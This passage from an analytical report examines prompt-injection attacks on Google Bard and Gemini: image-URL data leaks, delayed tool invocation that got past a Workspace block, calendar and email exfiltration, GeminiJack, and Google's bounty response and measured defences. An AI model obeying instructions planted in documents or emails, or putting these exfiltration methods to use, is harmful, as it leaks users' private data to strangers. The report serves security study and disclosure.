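Carta writes that he and Gardner took "our victim's emails", but the account's owner would have had to enter the request that Carta published. An attacker might trick someone into doing this, as in Samoilenko's copy-and-paste attack on ChatGPT, but Carta and Gardner did not demonstrate such a trick. The user would also have had a fair chance of noticing that the paragraph they were about to send Bard was about copying emails into image addresses.

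Thacker found another flaw during the contest and tested it fully between two users. He uploaded a picture to Bard from one account, then used a second account, which had no right to see the picture, to get Bard to describe it. The test needed no planted instructions and showed one user taking data from another. The published Gmail attack involved only one user, the owner of the mailbox.

The Google Doc attack comes closer to showing one user stealing another's data, because its instructions are in a file that someone else could have written. Carta says that it "goes a little bit further" than his own attack. But Rehberger deliberately pointed Bard to the document. A real victim would have had to do the same, or ask something that led the extension to fetch a stranger's file, and Rehberger did not measure how often that would happen.

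### Whether anyone showed the full chain

In a full attack, a stranger would use a document or message to obtain one of the victim's emails. Rehberger had already carried out an attack of this kind on ChatGPT. On 19 May, Willison (2023) called it the first working attack he had seen that stole private data through ChatGPT plugins. One plugin opened a web page containing planted instructions, which triggered a second plugin, Zapier, to retrieve the latest emails from Gmail. The first plugin then sent the data out in another web request.

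Rehberger's December talk showed attacks on both ChatGPT and Bard, so the two are easy to confuse. The stolen email in the talk comes from ChatGPT with the Zapier plugin. In the Bard demonstration, Rehberger says the goal is to take the text in the chat, and the attacker's file receives the line he had typed. The slides for the talk, *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS* (Rehberger, 2023), also keep the plugin and Bard demonstrations separate. He gave the talk again the following April, and the slides for that version, also titled *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS* (Rehberger, 2024), contain the same Bard demonstration with no stolen email.

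In *Trust No AI*, his later survey of his own findings, Rehberger lists Bard with ten other products that leaked data through images. His examples of attacks that took email from an inbox, however, involve the Zapier plugin and Microsoft 365 Copilot. If he had stolen an email through Bard, he would probably have reported it there.

HackerOne's account is less precise. In the list of steps, Singh writes that the document tricked Bard into encoding "personal data/information" in the image address, which a reader could take to include email. But when describing the impact, Singh mentions only chat history, which matches what Rehberger demonstrated.

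Rehberger got closer to a full attack chain in November 2023. He tested whether planted instructions could make Bard call its extensions, as described in Embrace the Red's *Google Gemini*. The instructions triggered Flights, Hotels and YouTube, but not Workspace. He concluded that once untrusted content had entered the conversation, Bard would not call the Workspace extension in the same answer.

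He got around the restriction by writing an email that told Bard to wait until the user made another request, then find a document about cats in the user's Drive and print it word for word. When the user asked Bard about the email and then asked something else, Bard called the Workspace extension and printed the document in the chat.

In this test, a stranger's email caused Bard to fetch a private file that the user had not asked for. The file's text appeared only on the user's own screen because Google had already fixed the image leak. The leak was open in September, but Rehberger does not say whether the Workspace extension was already restricted then, or whether delayed instructions would have bypassed the restriction. He demonstrated the two halves of a full attack on Bard about two months apart and never combined them in one run.

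A shorter route may also have worked without a second call to the extension. If a user asked Bard to summarise the day's emails and one of them was hostile, the extension would have fetched it along with the private ones. The hostile email could have contained an instruction to copy a sentence from another email into an image address. The two groups had separately shown that Bard would follow instructions in a fetched file and would copy an email into such an address. The combination would probably have worked at least some of the time, but neither group published a test of it, and Bard might have refused or failed to write the address correctly.

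### Which words could leave

Even without a second call, the Google Doc attack could have exposed part of an email the user had already discussed with Bard. For example, Dana opens a chat by typing, "Summarise the email from my landlord about the flat." Bard fetches the email and answers, "Your landlord is raising the rent to £1,450 from March and wants your answer by Friday. The new door code is 4471."

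Dana then asks, in the same chat, "What does the tenants' rights checklist cover?" The checklist is a document that a stranger shared with her, and it contains instructions like Rehberger's. If Bard counts the first 20 words from the top of the conversation, these words leave in the image address:

> Summarise the email from my landlord about the flat. Your landlord is raising the rent to £1,450 from March and

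The first nine words are Dana's and the other eleven come from Bard's summary. The stranger learns her new rent but not the door code. Rehberger's demonstration extracted only text that the user had typed, so it does not show whether Bard would have counted its own answers too. If Bard had counted only Dana's words, the stranger would have received her two requests, which total 16 words, and learned that her landlord had written to her about the flat.

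The words a user types can also be valuable. *Second Thoughts* gives the example of an employee who might start a chat by telling Bard that the company is making an offer for a named firm. An outsider who saw only the first ten words would know enough to buy the firm's shares before the price rose.

Rehberger chose the number 20 for a proof of concept, but a thief could have asked for something else. Second Thoughts suggests asking for a summary of the most sensitive parts of the conversation, and Rehberger had asked for passwords in his attack on Bing Chat. A similar request in the checklist could have sent Dana's door code to the stranger.

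It is less clear whether an attacker could have obtained details that Bard left out of its summary. The landlord's email, for example, might also have contained his bank details. If the full email stayed in the model's context after Bard answered, an attacker could have used the checklist to request them too. Google's help page is consistent with this, but neither group tested it. The rest of Dana's inbox was safer, because Bard had not fetched it and an attacker would have needed another call to the Workspace extension.

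Dana might not have been safe even if she had opened the checklist first and asked about the landlord's email afterwards. The planted text could have stayed in the context with an instruction for Bard to wait. Rehberger had made Bing Chat wait two turns before it leaked anything, and the instruction about the cat document took effect after one. Starting a new chat between the two requests would have helped by keeping the checklist and the email in separate conversations.

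### What a case report can prove

One successful exploit is enough to prove that a flaw exists. Rehberger proved that in September 2023 a Google Doc could control what Bard wrote, and that Bard's page would send part of the conversation to an outsider without a click. Carta and Gardner proved that Bard would copy an email into an image address, and that the request for that image could reach a server they had rented. Google did not dismiss either demonstration as theoretical, and could not reasonably have done so.

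Neither report gives a success rate. To measure one, a researcher would have to keep the text of the hostile document the same, test it many times with different conversations and questions, and count how often the right words arrived. Google could also change Bard at any time, so a rate measured one week might not have held the next. Rehberger's ten tries and his remark about the worked examples suggest that Bard was a somewhat awkward target, but they don't provide a percentage.

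The reports also give no estimate of how many people were at risk. The Google Doc attack could affect only people who had connected the Workspace extension and who brought a hostile file into a chat that contained something worth stealing.

Neither group reports that criminals used the flaw. This is weak evidence that none did, because researchers who test their own accounts cannot see attacks on other people's. Google was better placed to look for such attacks, since Rehberger's script and Gardner's server both ran on its services.

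The speed of the first attack shows that the flaw was easy for specialists to find. Rehberger had been using the same technique on other chatbots since April, and Thacker had spent the summer testing Bard. A criminal without their experience would probably have needed longer.

The US non-profit research organisation MITRE included the case in ATLAS, its public catalogue of attacks on AI systems. PromptRiskDB's *Google Bard Conversation Exfiltration*, a copy of the entry, labels it an "exercise", the catalogue's term for a demonstration by researchers rather than an attack on real victims. The entry covers Rehberger's attack but not Carta and Gardner's. It divides the attack into seven steps, three of them preparation, including writing the instructions and finding a script address that the CSP would allow. It describes the harm as the leak of the user's conversation, which could help an attacker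 target the user again, and does not report that any emails were stolen.

Willison (2023) linked to Rehberger's post on 4 November and called it the first reported prompt injection attack on Bard's access to personal documents. Rehberger's case supports Willison's view that such attacks were inevitable, but only for the injection itself. The data theft was easier to prevent, because both attacks, as published, depended on a CSP that trusted domains where the public could run programs, and Google could have written a narrower one.

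Willison also wanted to know how Google's fix worked and how well it would withstand variations of the attack. Carta and Gardner had already found a second way past the same policy, but they did not publish it until the following March.

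## How Google responded: the fix, the payments and the new reporting rules

Google took no more than 30 days to fix the leak that Rehberger reported, and it paid Carta and Gardner more than $21,000 for reporting theirs. A week after confirming the fix, it published detailed criteria for rewarding reports about its AI products. Google did nearly all of this through its Vulnerability Reward Program (VRP), which is aimed at security researchers.

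### From report to confirmed fix

Rehberger reported the Google Doc attack to the VRP on 19 September 2023. According to Embrace the Red, he asked about the report's status on 19 October because he wanted to show the attack at Ekoparty, a security conference. Google replied that it had fixed the flaw and that he could include the demonstration in his talk. His write-up was online by 4 November, when Willison linked to it.

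The date of the fix is unknown, but Google's reply to a question shows that it was in place by 19 October. Neither group of researchers mentions Google suspending the Workspace extension in the meantime, and users may have been exposed for a few days to a month. Carta writes that he and Gardner reported the Gmail attack promptly, but he doesn't say when Google fixed it.

Rehberger thanked Google's security and Bard teams for fixing the issue "promptly", and Singh described Google as "grateful". Singh had a commercial reason to describe the response favourably, because HackerOne sells bug-bounty services. Rehberger's praise is stronger evidence because he did not praise every company. He recalled in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that OpenAI had shown little interest in fixing the same kind of leak in ChatGPT in 2023, and it took about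 eight months to begin. Anthropic had closed his report on Claude in two weeks. Microsoft told him of its fix for Bing Chat after almost ten weeks, though he later dated the fix itself to May, about a month after his report. Google's 30 days were respectable for that year, but not exceptional.

### What Google changed

Google had not told Rehberger how the fix worked. He saw that Bard's CSP still permitted the same sites and that Bard still displayed images, so he inferred that Google had added a filter to keep data out of image addresses.

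Such a filter would check Bard's answer before the browser acted on it. It might, for example, delete any image line with text after a question mark in the address. An attacker could then put the stolen words in the image's file name, such as book-club-moved-to-Thursday.png, and the filter would need another rule. The filter's rules have to cover the different ways an attacker could write an address, whereas a CSP blocks every request to an unlisted site.

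Google could have relied on the CSP, as Microsoft had for Bing Chat, only by removing the domains where the public could run programs, and Bard may have needed some of them for legitimate pictures. A filter would have been less disruptive, but it left the browser able to contact both Rehberger's script and Gardner's server. It is also unclear whether one change stopped both attacks. If a filter had already caused Bard's refusals during the Gmail attack, the fix may have extended it.

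In a later account of Gemini's defences, Google said that a "markdown sanitizer" identifies external image URLs and does not display the images. The sanitizer may have developed from the 2023 fix, but Google did not say so.

It is also harder to be sure that a problem has been fixed in a language model than in most software. In Google's *Celebrating One Year of AI Bug Bounties at Alphabet*, the reward team wrote that it sometimes could not reproduce a well-written report accompanied by a clear video. A problem could disappear and come back as the company adjusted a model. When an attack failed, staff might not know whether the report was wrong, they had made a mistake, or the attack worked only once in a hundred tries. A filter on addresses is easier to test because the same address should get the same result each time. But passing this test would not show that Bard had stopped following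 instructions in documents.

### What Google paid, and for what

Carta and Gardner received $20,000 for the Gmail attack and a $1,337 bonus for the third "coolest bug" of the bugSWAT contest. The $50,000 in Carta's title is the total he, Gardner and Thacker earned from the contest. It includes $6,000 for a way to slow down part of Google Cloud by repeating one instruction up to a million times in a request. They received another $1,000 after Thacker asked how Google signed certain requests and an engineer found that the signing key was an ordinary sentence written into the source code.

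No payment to Rehberger's group is documented. Google counted the Google Doc attack among the contest's 35 reports, which earned more than $87,000 in total. We can't work out what Rehberger and Greshake received by subtracting Carta's $50,000, because Thacker belonged to both groups and Carta does not say whether the $50,000 includes Thacker's share of any reward for the Google Doc attack.

The VRP's general rules help explain why Google paid $20,000 for the Gmail attack, although the surviving copy of the rules dates from February 2025 and may differ from the 2023 version. Google normally pays nothing for a redirect from one of its addresses to another site. It also excludes flaws in the programs that cloud customers run under googleusercontent.com. Carta and Gardner earned the reward by combining a redirect and a customer's server, neither of which would ordinarily have qualified, with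 an assistant that could read email.

Google's rules also exclude bugs that need "exceedingly unlikely user interaction", such as a victim typing hostile code into Google Maps. The published Gmail attack needed the victim to type a whole paragraph of instructions. Google paid anyway, probably because its engineers recognised that the instructions could come from somewhere else, as Rehberger's document had shown. The general rules allow the panel to consider the greatest harm a flaw could cause, even if the reporter has not fully identified it.

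Google did not always pay for reports of flaws it fixed. Rehberger later reported a similar image leak in Google Colab, a service for writing and running code in shared notebooks. He expected Google to start giving the assistant the notebook's contents, which would make the leak serious. According to Embrace The Red, Google did not pay him, but it had fixed the leak by the time it made that change. Google therefore closed Colab's image channel before connecting it to untrusted content, whereas it closed Bard's afterwards.

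### Outside testing before and after the launch

For months, Google had been inviting outsiders to test Bard. In an entry dated 16 May 2023 on its site for bug hunters, Google said it would reward reports about the chatbot under the Abuse VRP, the part of its vulnerability reward program that covers harmful uses of a product's features. The entry now uses the chatbot's later name, Gemini. Thacker and Gardner applied to bugSWAT in June, and by the August meeting in Las Vegas, Thacker had found the flaw that let one user get Bard to describe another user's pictures.

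Google let hackers question engineers who could read the source code, which companies hoping to avoid bad news don't usually do. This is good evidence that Google wanted outsiders to find flaws. It also extended the contest to the end of September, which kept motivated specialists at work when it launched the extensions.

However, these specialists do not seem to have had early access to the Workspace extension. Thacker and Rehberger both seem to have learned of it from the public announcement, and the people who found the leak could start only when the public could connect their mailboxes. Google may have had other testers under confidentiality agreements, and its own staff may have tried planted instructions. Giving the same contestants the extension a week earlier might well have exposed the leak before any user was at risk, since Rehberger needed less than a day.

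### Whether the 2023 criteria covered theft

On 26 October 2023, a week after confirming to Rehberger that the fix was in place, Google (2023) published its criteria for reports about AI products. Google presented the criteria as part of the voluntary commitments it had made at the White House in July, and it had announced in September that it would expand the program. The timing therefore does not show that the Bard attacks prompted the criteria. Google drew the categories from the report by Fabian and Crisp.

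The criteria took the form of a table of attacks, each marked in or out of scope. Two entries for prompt injection were in scope:

- injections "invisible to victims" that change the state of a victim's account or any of their assets;
- injections into tools whose response someone uses to make decisions that directly affect victims.

Suppose the tenants' rights checklist that a stranger shared with Dana makes her assistant delete her landlord's email. This changes the state of her account, so the attack fits the first entry. Now suppose her landlord uses an AI tool to rank applicants for another flat, and one applicant's letter contains a hidden instruction to rank that applicant first. If he picks his tenant from the ranking, the attack fits the second entry.

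Theft by reading alone fits neither entry well. In Rehberger's attack, the checklist would send Dana's new rent to the stranger but leave her emails and files unchanged. Nobody would have used Bard's answer to make a decision about her, unless the browser loading a picture counts, which is a strained reading. The second entry is a much better fit for the first example in Fabian and Crisp's report, in which a fraudster gets an AI filter to pass a bad email.

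The omission is odd because two groups had just shown Google that Bard could leak private text. An injection could hardly have used the Workspace extension to alter someone's mailbox, the harm in the first entry, because the extension was apparently read-only. Elsewhere in the table, Google accepted reports of attacks that extracted sensitive training data, the exact weights of a confidential model, or sensitive information from the developer's standing instructions, but it did not list a user's own emails and documents.

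Such theft was still eligible for a reward. An entry near the end of the table covered any other flaw in an AI product that clearly met the program's usual standard for a security or abuse issue. In the 2025 copy of the general rules, that standard includes any design flaw that substantially affects the "confidentiality or integrity of user data". An attack that sends part of a private conversation to a stranger meets that standard. Google's payment to Carta and Gardner also shows that it was willing to reward such reports.

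A researcher who knew the general rules would therefore have reported a leak like Bard's, but someone who read only the two entries on injection might have concluded that Google wanted attacks that changed something, and spent their time on those. The table also listed "jailbreaks", prompts that get a chatbot to produce forbidden content in the user's own session, as out of scope. A newcomer could easily have confused these with injections, since both use text to make a model misbehave.

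The general rules probably determined the amount as well. Carta and Gardner received $20,000, well above the standard maximum of $13,337 for abuse reports in the March 2025 copy of Google's *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules*. The panel could pay more for unusually clever findings, and bugSWAT may have had its own scale. But $20,000 was within the range for a security flaw, since Crouse (2023), in *Google Offers Bug Bounties for Generative AI Security Vulnerabilities*, gave $31,337 as the program's maximum for AI flaws at the time.

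### The revision of October 2025

The March 2025 rules have the same two entries on prompt injection that Google first published almost a year and a half earlier. On 6 October 2025, *How we're securing the AI frontier* (Kotsovinos and Flynn, 2025) announced a separate reward program for AI, with a single set of rules for security and abuse. Kotsovinos and Flynn said the program would clarify which problems were in scope.

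SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program* reports that the new program pays up to $15,000 for attacks on Google's most important products that leak sensitive information without the user's approval. Attacks that modify a victim's account or data earn up to $20,000. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Launches AI Bug Bounty with $30,000 Top Reward* lists Gemini, Gmail and Drive among those products, and reports that multipliers can raise the top reward by half. OODA Loop described one of Google's examples of a qualifying bug, an injection that summarises all of someone's email and sends the summary to the attacker's account. This example closely resembles the full attack that neither group had demonstrated on Bard in 2023.

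SecurityWeek and Infosecurity Magazine also reported that prompt injections were out of scope, which seems to contradict the example. The likely explanation is that Google judges a report by the harm it demonstrates. A planted sentence that makes Gemini talk like a pirate is a content problem, which Google asks users to report with the feedback button, while one that makes Gemini send out the user's email is data theft. At the DEF CON 34 hacker conference in 2026, Kotheimer and Di Bartolo of Google confirmed this reading in *Google's AI Vulnerability Reward Program (AI VRP)*, which listed "sensitive data exfiltration" caused by indirect prompt injection among the program's subjects.

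Under the 2025 rules, a researcher could find the Bard attack in the list instead of relying on a catch-all category. Google had already paid for one such attack two years earlier, so the change doesn't prove that it had undervalued them. The change may have had several causes, including Gemini's growing access to private data and two years of questions from researchers about what qualified.

### What the program's figures measure

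In the first year after it published the AI criteria, Google received over 140 reports about its generative AI products and paid more than $50,000. About one in six reports, or roughly 23, led a product team to make a change that reduced the risk. Google said the rate was similar across its wider reward program. Many researchers reported jailbreaks and other out-of-scope problems, so the remaining reports did not necessarily describe flaws that Google had left open.

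Google's regular program paid an average of around $360 per report. Google paid about $2,500 each for the 35 reports in the bugSWAT contest, and the payment for the Gmail attack alone equaled about two-fifths of the regular program's first-year total. A small group of invited specialists with access to Google's engineers evidently produced more valuable findings than an open call, though the contest also paid bonuses that raised its average.

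Google (2025) gave slightly later figures in its review of 2024, over 150 reports and $55,000, and listed the contest separately. The contest figures are identical to those in the previous year's review and refer to the same 2023 event, so adding up the two reviews would count it twice.

Google's spending then grew quickly. Kotsovinos and Flynn put total rewards for AI-related issues at over $430,000 by October 2025. Most of the increase probably came from one contest in Tokyo that April, for which Google's *VRP 2025 Year in Review* lists more than 70 reports and over $400,000. TechRadar's *Google paid over $17 million to bug hunters in 2025* gives a later total of $890,000. These amounts show that Google increasingly valued outside research on AI, but they are a poor measure of how safe its assistants were, because payouts can rise when products have more flaws, when more people look for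 them, or when the company raises its rates.

### Repair and disclosure

Google openly credited the researchers. Its 2023 and 2024 reviews both list the two Bard reports by title, and the first also gives the researchers' first names. The reward team's motto is "we buy bugs, not silence", and Google followed it here by clearing Rehberger to present his attack as soon as he asked.

Google's two reviews do not explain what had gone wrong. Someone who had used Bard in September 2023 would learn from them that hackers had found a way "From Prompt Injection to Data Exfiltration", but would have to read the researchers' posts to learn that an attacker could have used a shared document to steal part of a conversation. The researchers' write-ups, HackerOne's account and Google's reviews contain no advisory, notice to users or statement about affected accounts, though Google may have issued one elsewhere.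 It is also not known whether the company searched its records for other people using the same technique.

A company can have fair reasons for saying little about a repaired flaw. Google could fix Bard on its own servers, so users had no update to install. A detailed description of the filter would have helped attackers look for gaps in it. If Google had checked and found no victims, notifying everyone who had connected a mailbox could have alarmed them without giving them anything to do.

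These reasons apply to the image leak, which Google could close. They are weaker for the wider risk that an assistant will follow instructions in other people's documents. Google had not removed that risk, as the unresolved flaw in the Google Docs writing feature showed. Users could guard against it only if they knew about it, and Google could have warned them without revealing any detail about the filter.

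On 26 October, Richardson and Hansen (2023) introduced the new criteria to a general audience in *Acting on our commitment to safe and secure AI*. They wrote that outside researchers discover some of the biggest vulnerabilities, and listed unfair bias, model manipulation and hallucinations among the new concerns raised by generative AI. This was an obvious occasion to mention the Bard reports, but they did not. Rehberger had not yet published, so naming his case might have been premature, but they could have described the general risk without it. The criteria available to bug hunters that day described injections "invisible to victims", but the copy of Bard's help page from that month did not warn users about them.

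Google's 2025 reward rules also gave researchers little financial reason to press for better warnings. Google offered $100 to $500 for a report of incorrect documentation that was likely to leave users insecure, but only a credit on its website for a report of insufficient documentation. It would probably have classed the gap in Bard's help page as insufficient documentation.

Google has since disclosed a security risk before fixing it. In November 2025, Willison (2025) noted that the bug-hunter page for Antigravity, Google's programming tool, listed data exfiltration through prompt injection as a known issue that the company was working to fix. Because the issue was listed, researchers could not claim a reward for reporting it. Ordinary users were unlikely to look at the page, but anyone who did could learn about the risk while Google was still working on a fix.

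## What later tests of Bard and Gemini found

The October 2023 fix stopped attackers from using images to send data out of Bard, but planted instructions could still control what Bard wrote. Outside researchers kept testing the chatbot before and after Google renamed it Gemini. In 2024, their attacks mostly got it to deceive its own user. In 2025, they extracted private data again, through new routes and, in one product, through images.

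### A block on the Workspace extension

In November 2023 Rehberger had found that planted instructions could not make Bard call the Workspace extension in the same answer. So he used delayed tool invocation, in which the assistant calls an extension only after the user's next message, to get Bard to print the document about cats.

The delay worked because the block seems to have lasted only one turn, while the planted sentence stayed in the context. Rehberger wrote on Embrace the Red that the block was an interesting approach that other companies had not yet adopted. He reported the gap to Google that November, and Google confirmed that it was tracking the issue. When he published the tests in 2024, he still did not know what Google planned to do about it.

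Rehberger inferred that Google had foreseen the threat, but his tests do not distinguish this from a more mundane explanation. Bard may have needed an explicit request for something from Workspace before it would open a mailbox, as Google's help page of May 2024 suggests. An instruction planted in a picture would then have failed without such a request, whether or not Google had attackers in mind. In the cat test, the user had already asked about an email, so the later call would have met this requirement.

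The date of the block is also unknown. The September attacks cannot be used to date it, because neither tested whether Bard would open a mailbox on a stranger's instructions.

The date Google added the block affects how to read the launch documents. If the block was there on 19 September as a defence against attackers, Google's engineers had prepared for hostile documents while its help page warned users only about made-up answers and outdated emails. The missing warning would then look more like a choice, or at least a failure to pass on what the engineers knew, than ignorance. If Google added the block in October, its response to the September reports went beyond closing the image leak.

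### Getting the user to hand it over

HiddenLayer, an AI security company, tested Gemini in 2024 with a file in Google Drive. According to SC Media's *Google Gemini bugs enable prompt leaks, injection via Workspace plugin*, a user who asked to see the file got a reply demanding the "document password". The company also got Gemini to write a poem about the theft, mocking any user who complied. Nothing left the account, but HiddenLayer raised the possibility that an attacker could have Gemini add the password to a web address.

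A spokesperson for the company also suggested that a stranger might get Gemini to open the file by naming it after something the target is working on, such as a travel itinerary. Below its answer, Gemini listed the Drive files it had considered, which might alert a careful user to an unfamiliar one. HiddenLayer said answers based on email had no such list.

Google told SC Media that it trained its models against prompt injection and that spam filters in Gmail and Drive helped keep hostile prompts out. It also said it had no evidence that anyone had used these flaws to harm Gemini users.

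The security company WithSecure tried an attack by email instead. Capitella's *When your AI Assistant has an evil twin* describes how the user asked Gemini to summarise recent mail. Gemini did so, then announced a new version of itself and gave the user a code to activate it. The code was a lightly disguised secret from a different email. A user who submitted the code would have sent the secret to the attacker.

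One email had therefore caused Gemini to extract a secret from another email, an attack nobody had demonstrated on Bard in 2023. The attack may not have had to bypass the block on Workspace, because Gemini may already have fetched both emails to answer the request for a summary.

Capitella also tried the 2023 method. Each attempt to produce an image with data in its URL ended the chat session with an error, and links with data in the URL failed too. This is the best outside evidence that Google's fix held, though he could see only that his own variants didn't work. It explains why he had to rely on a trick that needed the user's help.

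He reported the attack on 19 May 2024. Google classed it as an abuse risk on 30 May, and said the next day that it knew of the issue and would not fix it for the moment. That answer is more defensible than it sounds, because a false announcement from Gemini is made of ordinary sentences, which are harder for a program to recognise and block than an image address.

In July 2025 a researcher reporting through 0din, Mozilla's bug-bounty programme for AI, got a similar result from Gemini's email summaries. Hidden text in an email made Gemini include the sender's false warning in its summary. The attack again depended on the reader believing what Gemini wrote.

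### Data leaves again

In *Invitation Is All You Need!*, Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025) got data out of Gemini without asking the user to hand it over. They sent calendar invitations with instructions in the titles. When the user asked about upcoming events, Gemini read the titles and composed a web address containing the names of the user's meetings. When the user then thanked Gemini, the phone's browser opened the address, sending six meeting titles to a server that logged them. In a second version, the researchers put the instructions in an email's subject line and extracted the subject of another email.

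As in 2023, the attack put private words in an address, but this time it was the address of a web page that Gemini could open through an Android phone's browser. The attack also used a delay again. Google had divided Gemini into a coordinating model and separate agents for the calendar, mail, home devices and other services, and only the coordinator could start an agent. The calendar agent passed the planted title to the coordinator with its results, and the coordinator acted on it after the user's next message.

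Nassi and colleagues list 14 attack scenarios, including opening a smart window and streaming video of the user. They took one from an earlier blog post, and they describe another, an email worm, as something attackers could build on the data theft. They rated ten of the 14 as high risk or worse, which is 71 per cent, though they give the figure as 73. The ratings combine the harm an attack could do with the skill, equipment and time needed to prepare it, and do not measure how often it succeeds. The researchers worked only on their own accounts and did not publish success rates.

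Google received the researchers' findings on 22 February 2025 and asked for 90 days to develop defences. In a statement that June, it said it had sped up that work and deployed protections such as user confirmations for sensitive actions. It also described the techniques as "theoretical", although the researchers had filmed the attacks in a working product.

The attack most similar to the Google Doc attack was GeminiJack, which Noma Security published in December 2025. It affected Gemini Enterprise, Google's assistant for organisations, and Vertex AI Search, a related search service. In an example from SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data*, an outsider shares a document about budgets, and an employee later asks Gemini to show the company's budgets. Gemini fetches the outsider's document along with the real ones and follows the instructions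 in it. It searches the organisation's mail, calendars and files for whatever the outsider named, then puts the results in the address of an image. When the employee's browser requests the image, it sends the results to the outsider.

Nobody had demonstrated this full chain on Bard: a stranger's document, an unrequested search of the user's private mail, and an image that sent out the results. Noma recorded a working theft on video, according to SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise*, and Google confirmed to SecurityWeek that Noma's description was accurate.

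Gemini Enterprise may have been less well protected in one respect than Bard was at its launch. Bard's Content Security Policy had forced both groups to find a host on a Google domain. In the accounts of GeminiJack, the browser loads the picture from the attacker's own server, and no host on a Google domain is mentioned. Google had been blocking data in image addresses in the consumer version of Gemini since at least May 2024, when Capitella ran into the block, but it had evidently not extended this protection to every product that read email.

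Some claims about GeminiJack are overstated. Paganini (2025), in *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration*, wrote that one injection could take years of email and entire document stores. A web address is too short to hold that much data, so a thief would have needed a great many requests or would have had to choose what to take. The attack was "zero-click" only in that the employee clicked nothing unusual, and it still depended on a search that happened to bring up the planted document.

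The press also disagreed about when Noma reported the flaw. SecurityWeek gave May and SC Media gave June, probably because Noma wrote the date as 05/06/25. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* adds that Google confirmed receipt only in August. Google had completed the fix by November, so it took at least five months, compared with at most 30 days for Bard.

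Google made a bigger repair this time, changing how Gemini Enterprise and Vertex AI Search worked with their retrieval systems and separating the two products altogether. Noma wrote that the fix dealt with the core problem, the confusion of instructions with content. Its research lead, Sasi Levi, told SC Media that Google had not disclosed the technical details, which makes Noma's claim hard to check.

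A month later another security company, Miggo, used the calendar to extract data. The Hacker News' *Google Gemini Prompt Injection Flaw Exposed Private Calendar Data via Malicious Invites* (2026) describes an invitation with instructions in its description field. When the user asked about their schedule, Gemini summarised a day's private meetings, saved the summary in a new calendar event and gave the user a harmless answer. In many companies' calendars the attacker could read the new event. The data never appeared in a web address, so a filter on images and links would not have caught the leak. Miggo's researchers said that Google had confirmed and mitigated the flaw, according to Mint's *Researchers find Google Gemini can be used to steal your private data*.

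In June 2026 SafeBreach, where Yair works, disclosed an attack through phone notifications. The apps that could deliver it include WhatsApp and Slack (Fadilpašić, *Hackers could use poisoned WhatsApp and Slack notifications*, 2026). The Chinese technology site IT之家 adds text messages, and reports that the attackers' instructions were in foreign-language text or in links that the voice assistant did not read aloud (*谷歌Gemini语音助理曝漏洞，黑客利用通知信息为AI“下毒”*, 2026).

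A DoNews brief, *谷歌Gemini曝新型‘伪上下文对齐’漏洞* (2026), describes the attack as a way round Gemini's protection against delayed tool invocation, in which users approved actions without realising it, and dates Google's mitigation to mid-November 2025. It lists control of smart-home devices and changes to contacts as harms, but not theft of mail. DoNews labels the brief as machine-written, so these details need confirmation. If they are right, Google had by then built a defence against the technique Rehberger reported in 2023, and researchers had found a way past it.

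### What Google measured

Google has tested its own models against indirect injection since early 2024. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (Shi, Lin and colleagues, May 2025) describes the method and reports some of the results, including the only attack success rates for Gemini among the tests covered here.

Suppose Dana gives Gemini her passport number while planning a trip, then asks it to summarise her latest email. An attacker sent that email, which contains an instruction to send the number to the attacker's address. The attack succeeds if Gemini calls its email function with that address and the correct number, and fails if Gemini sends a blank or only describes what it would send.

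The researchers generated 2,000 conversations of this kind for each scenario, with a different private item in each. They used some to develop the planted text and kept 500 aside as a test. The attacker did not know the private item in advance, so the same text had to work on conversations it had never met:

attack success rate = test conversations in which the private item left ÷ all test conversations

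For each attack method, the researchers reported the success rate of the best planted text that method had found, so the figures reflect a determined attacker rather than an average one.

The researchers compared three automated methods of writing attack texts. In TAP, one model writes many candidate texts and keeps those that bring Gemini's response closest to the intended call. In Actor-Critic, one model proposes a text and another suggests improvements, guided by how likely Gemini is to comply. Beam Search starts from a plain request and adds random fragments, keeping any that make Gemini more likely to comply. In every scenario, at least one method had a success rate above 70 per cent against a version of Gemini 2.0 Flash without defences. Developing a highly successful text cost less than $10.

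Google then trained Gemini 2.5 on such attacks. It collected thousands of successful attack texts and paired them with responses in which the model ignored the planted instruction and did what the user had asked. It also used reinforcement learning, in which a model learns from rewards. The training data included attacks through the email function but none through the calendar function, so the calendar scenario tested whether the training also helped against attacks through a function it had not covered. The table gives the success rates for stealing a passport number, with new attacks developed against each model.

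| Scenario | Method | Gemini 2.0 | Gemini 2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email | TAP | 99.8% | 53.6% |
| Email | Actor-Critic | 66.2% | 40.8% |
| Email | Beam Search | 74.8% | 4.2% |
| Calendar | TAP | 100% | 94.6% |
| Calendar | Actor-Critic | 96.8% | 59.6% |
| Calendar | Beam Search | 98.6% | 0% |

Shi and colleagues summarise this as an average reduction of about 47 per cent, but the figure is in percentage points. The average attack success rate fell from 89 to 42 per cent, a drop of slightly more than half. Training nearly eliminated attacks that relied on random fragments but did much less against fluent text. In the calendar scenario, the most effective fluent text still worked in about 473 of 500 conversations.

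When the researchers reused 1,799 prompts containing attacks developed against Gemini 2.0, the success rate fell from 92 per cent on that model to 18 per cent on Gemini 2.5. They wrote that without further attacks adapted to Gemini 2.5, they would have overestimated its robustness. A real attacker can also adapt, by trying variations on their own account until one works.

They found the same with defences outside the model. They tried eight on Gemini 2.0, and in 16 of 24 combinations of defence and attack method, attacks adapted to the defence did at least as well as attacks that weren't. One of the best defences was a warning, placed after the retrieved text, not to reveal private information. In the calendar scenario, it limited TAP's success rate to 10.8 per cent on Gemini 2.0 and 6.2 per cent on Gemini 2.5. But a blanket warning could also stop Gemini from sending Dana's passport number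 to a travel agent when she asks it to.

### Rates and routes

The measured rates do not measure the chance that a Gemini user will lose data. The researchers assumed that Gemini had already fetched the hostile text, and they tested the model without the protections that Google adds in the finished product. Both choices raise the rates above what an attacker would achieve in practice. Other limits make the tests understate the risk. The scenarios called for only one extra function call, and the tests used mostly text. The final evaluation also used the same attack methods that had supplied the training data, so an attacker with a different method might do better.

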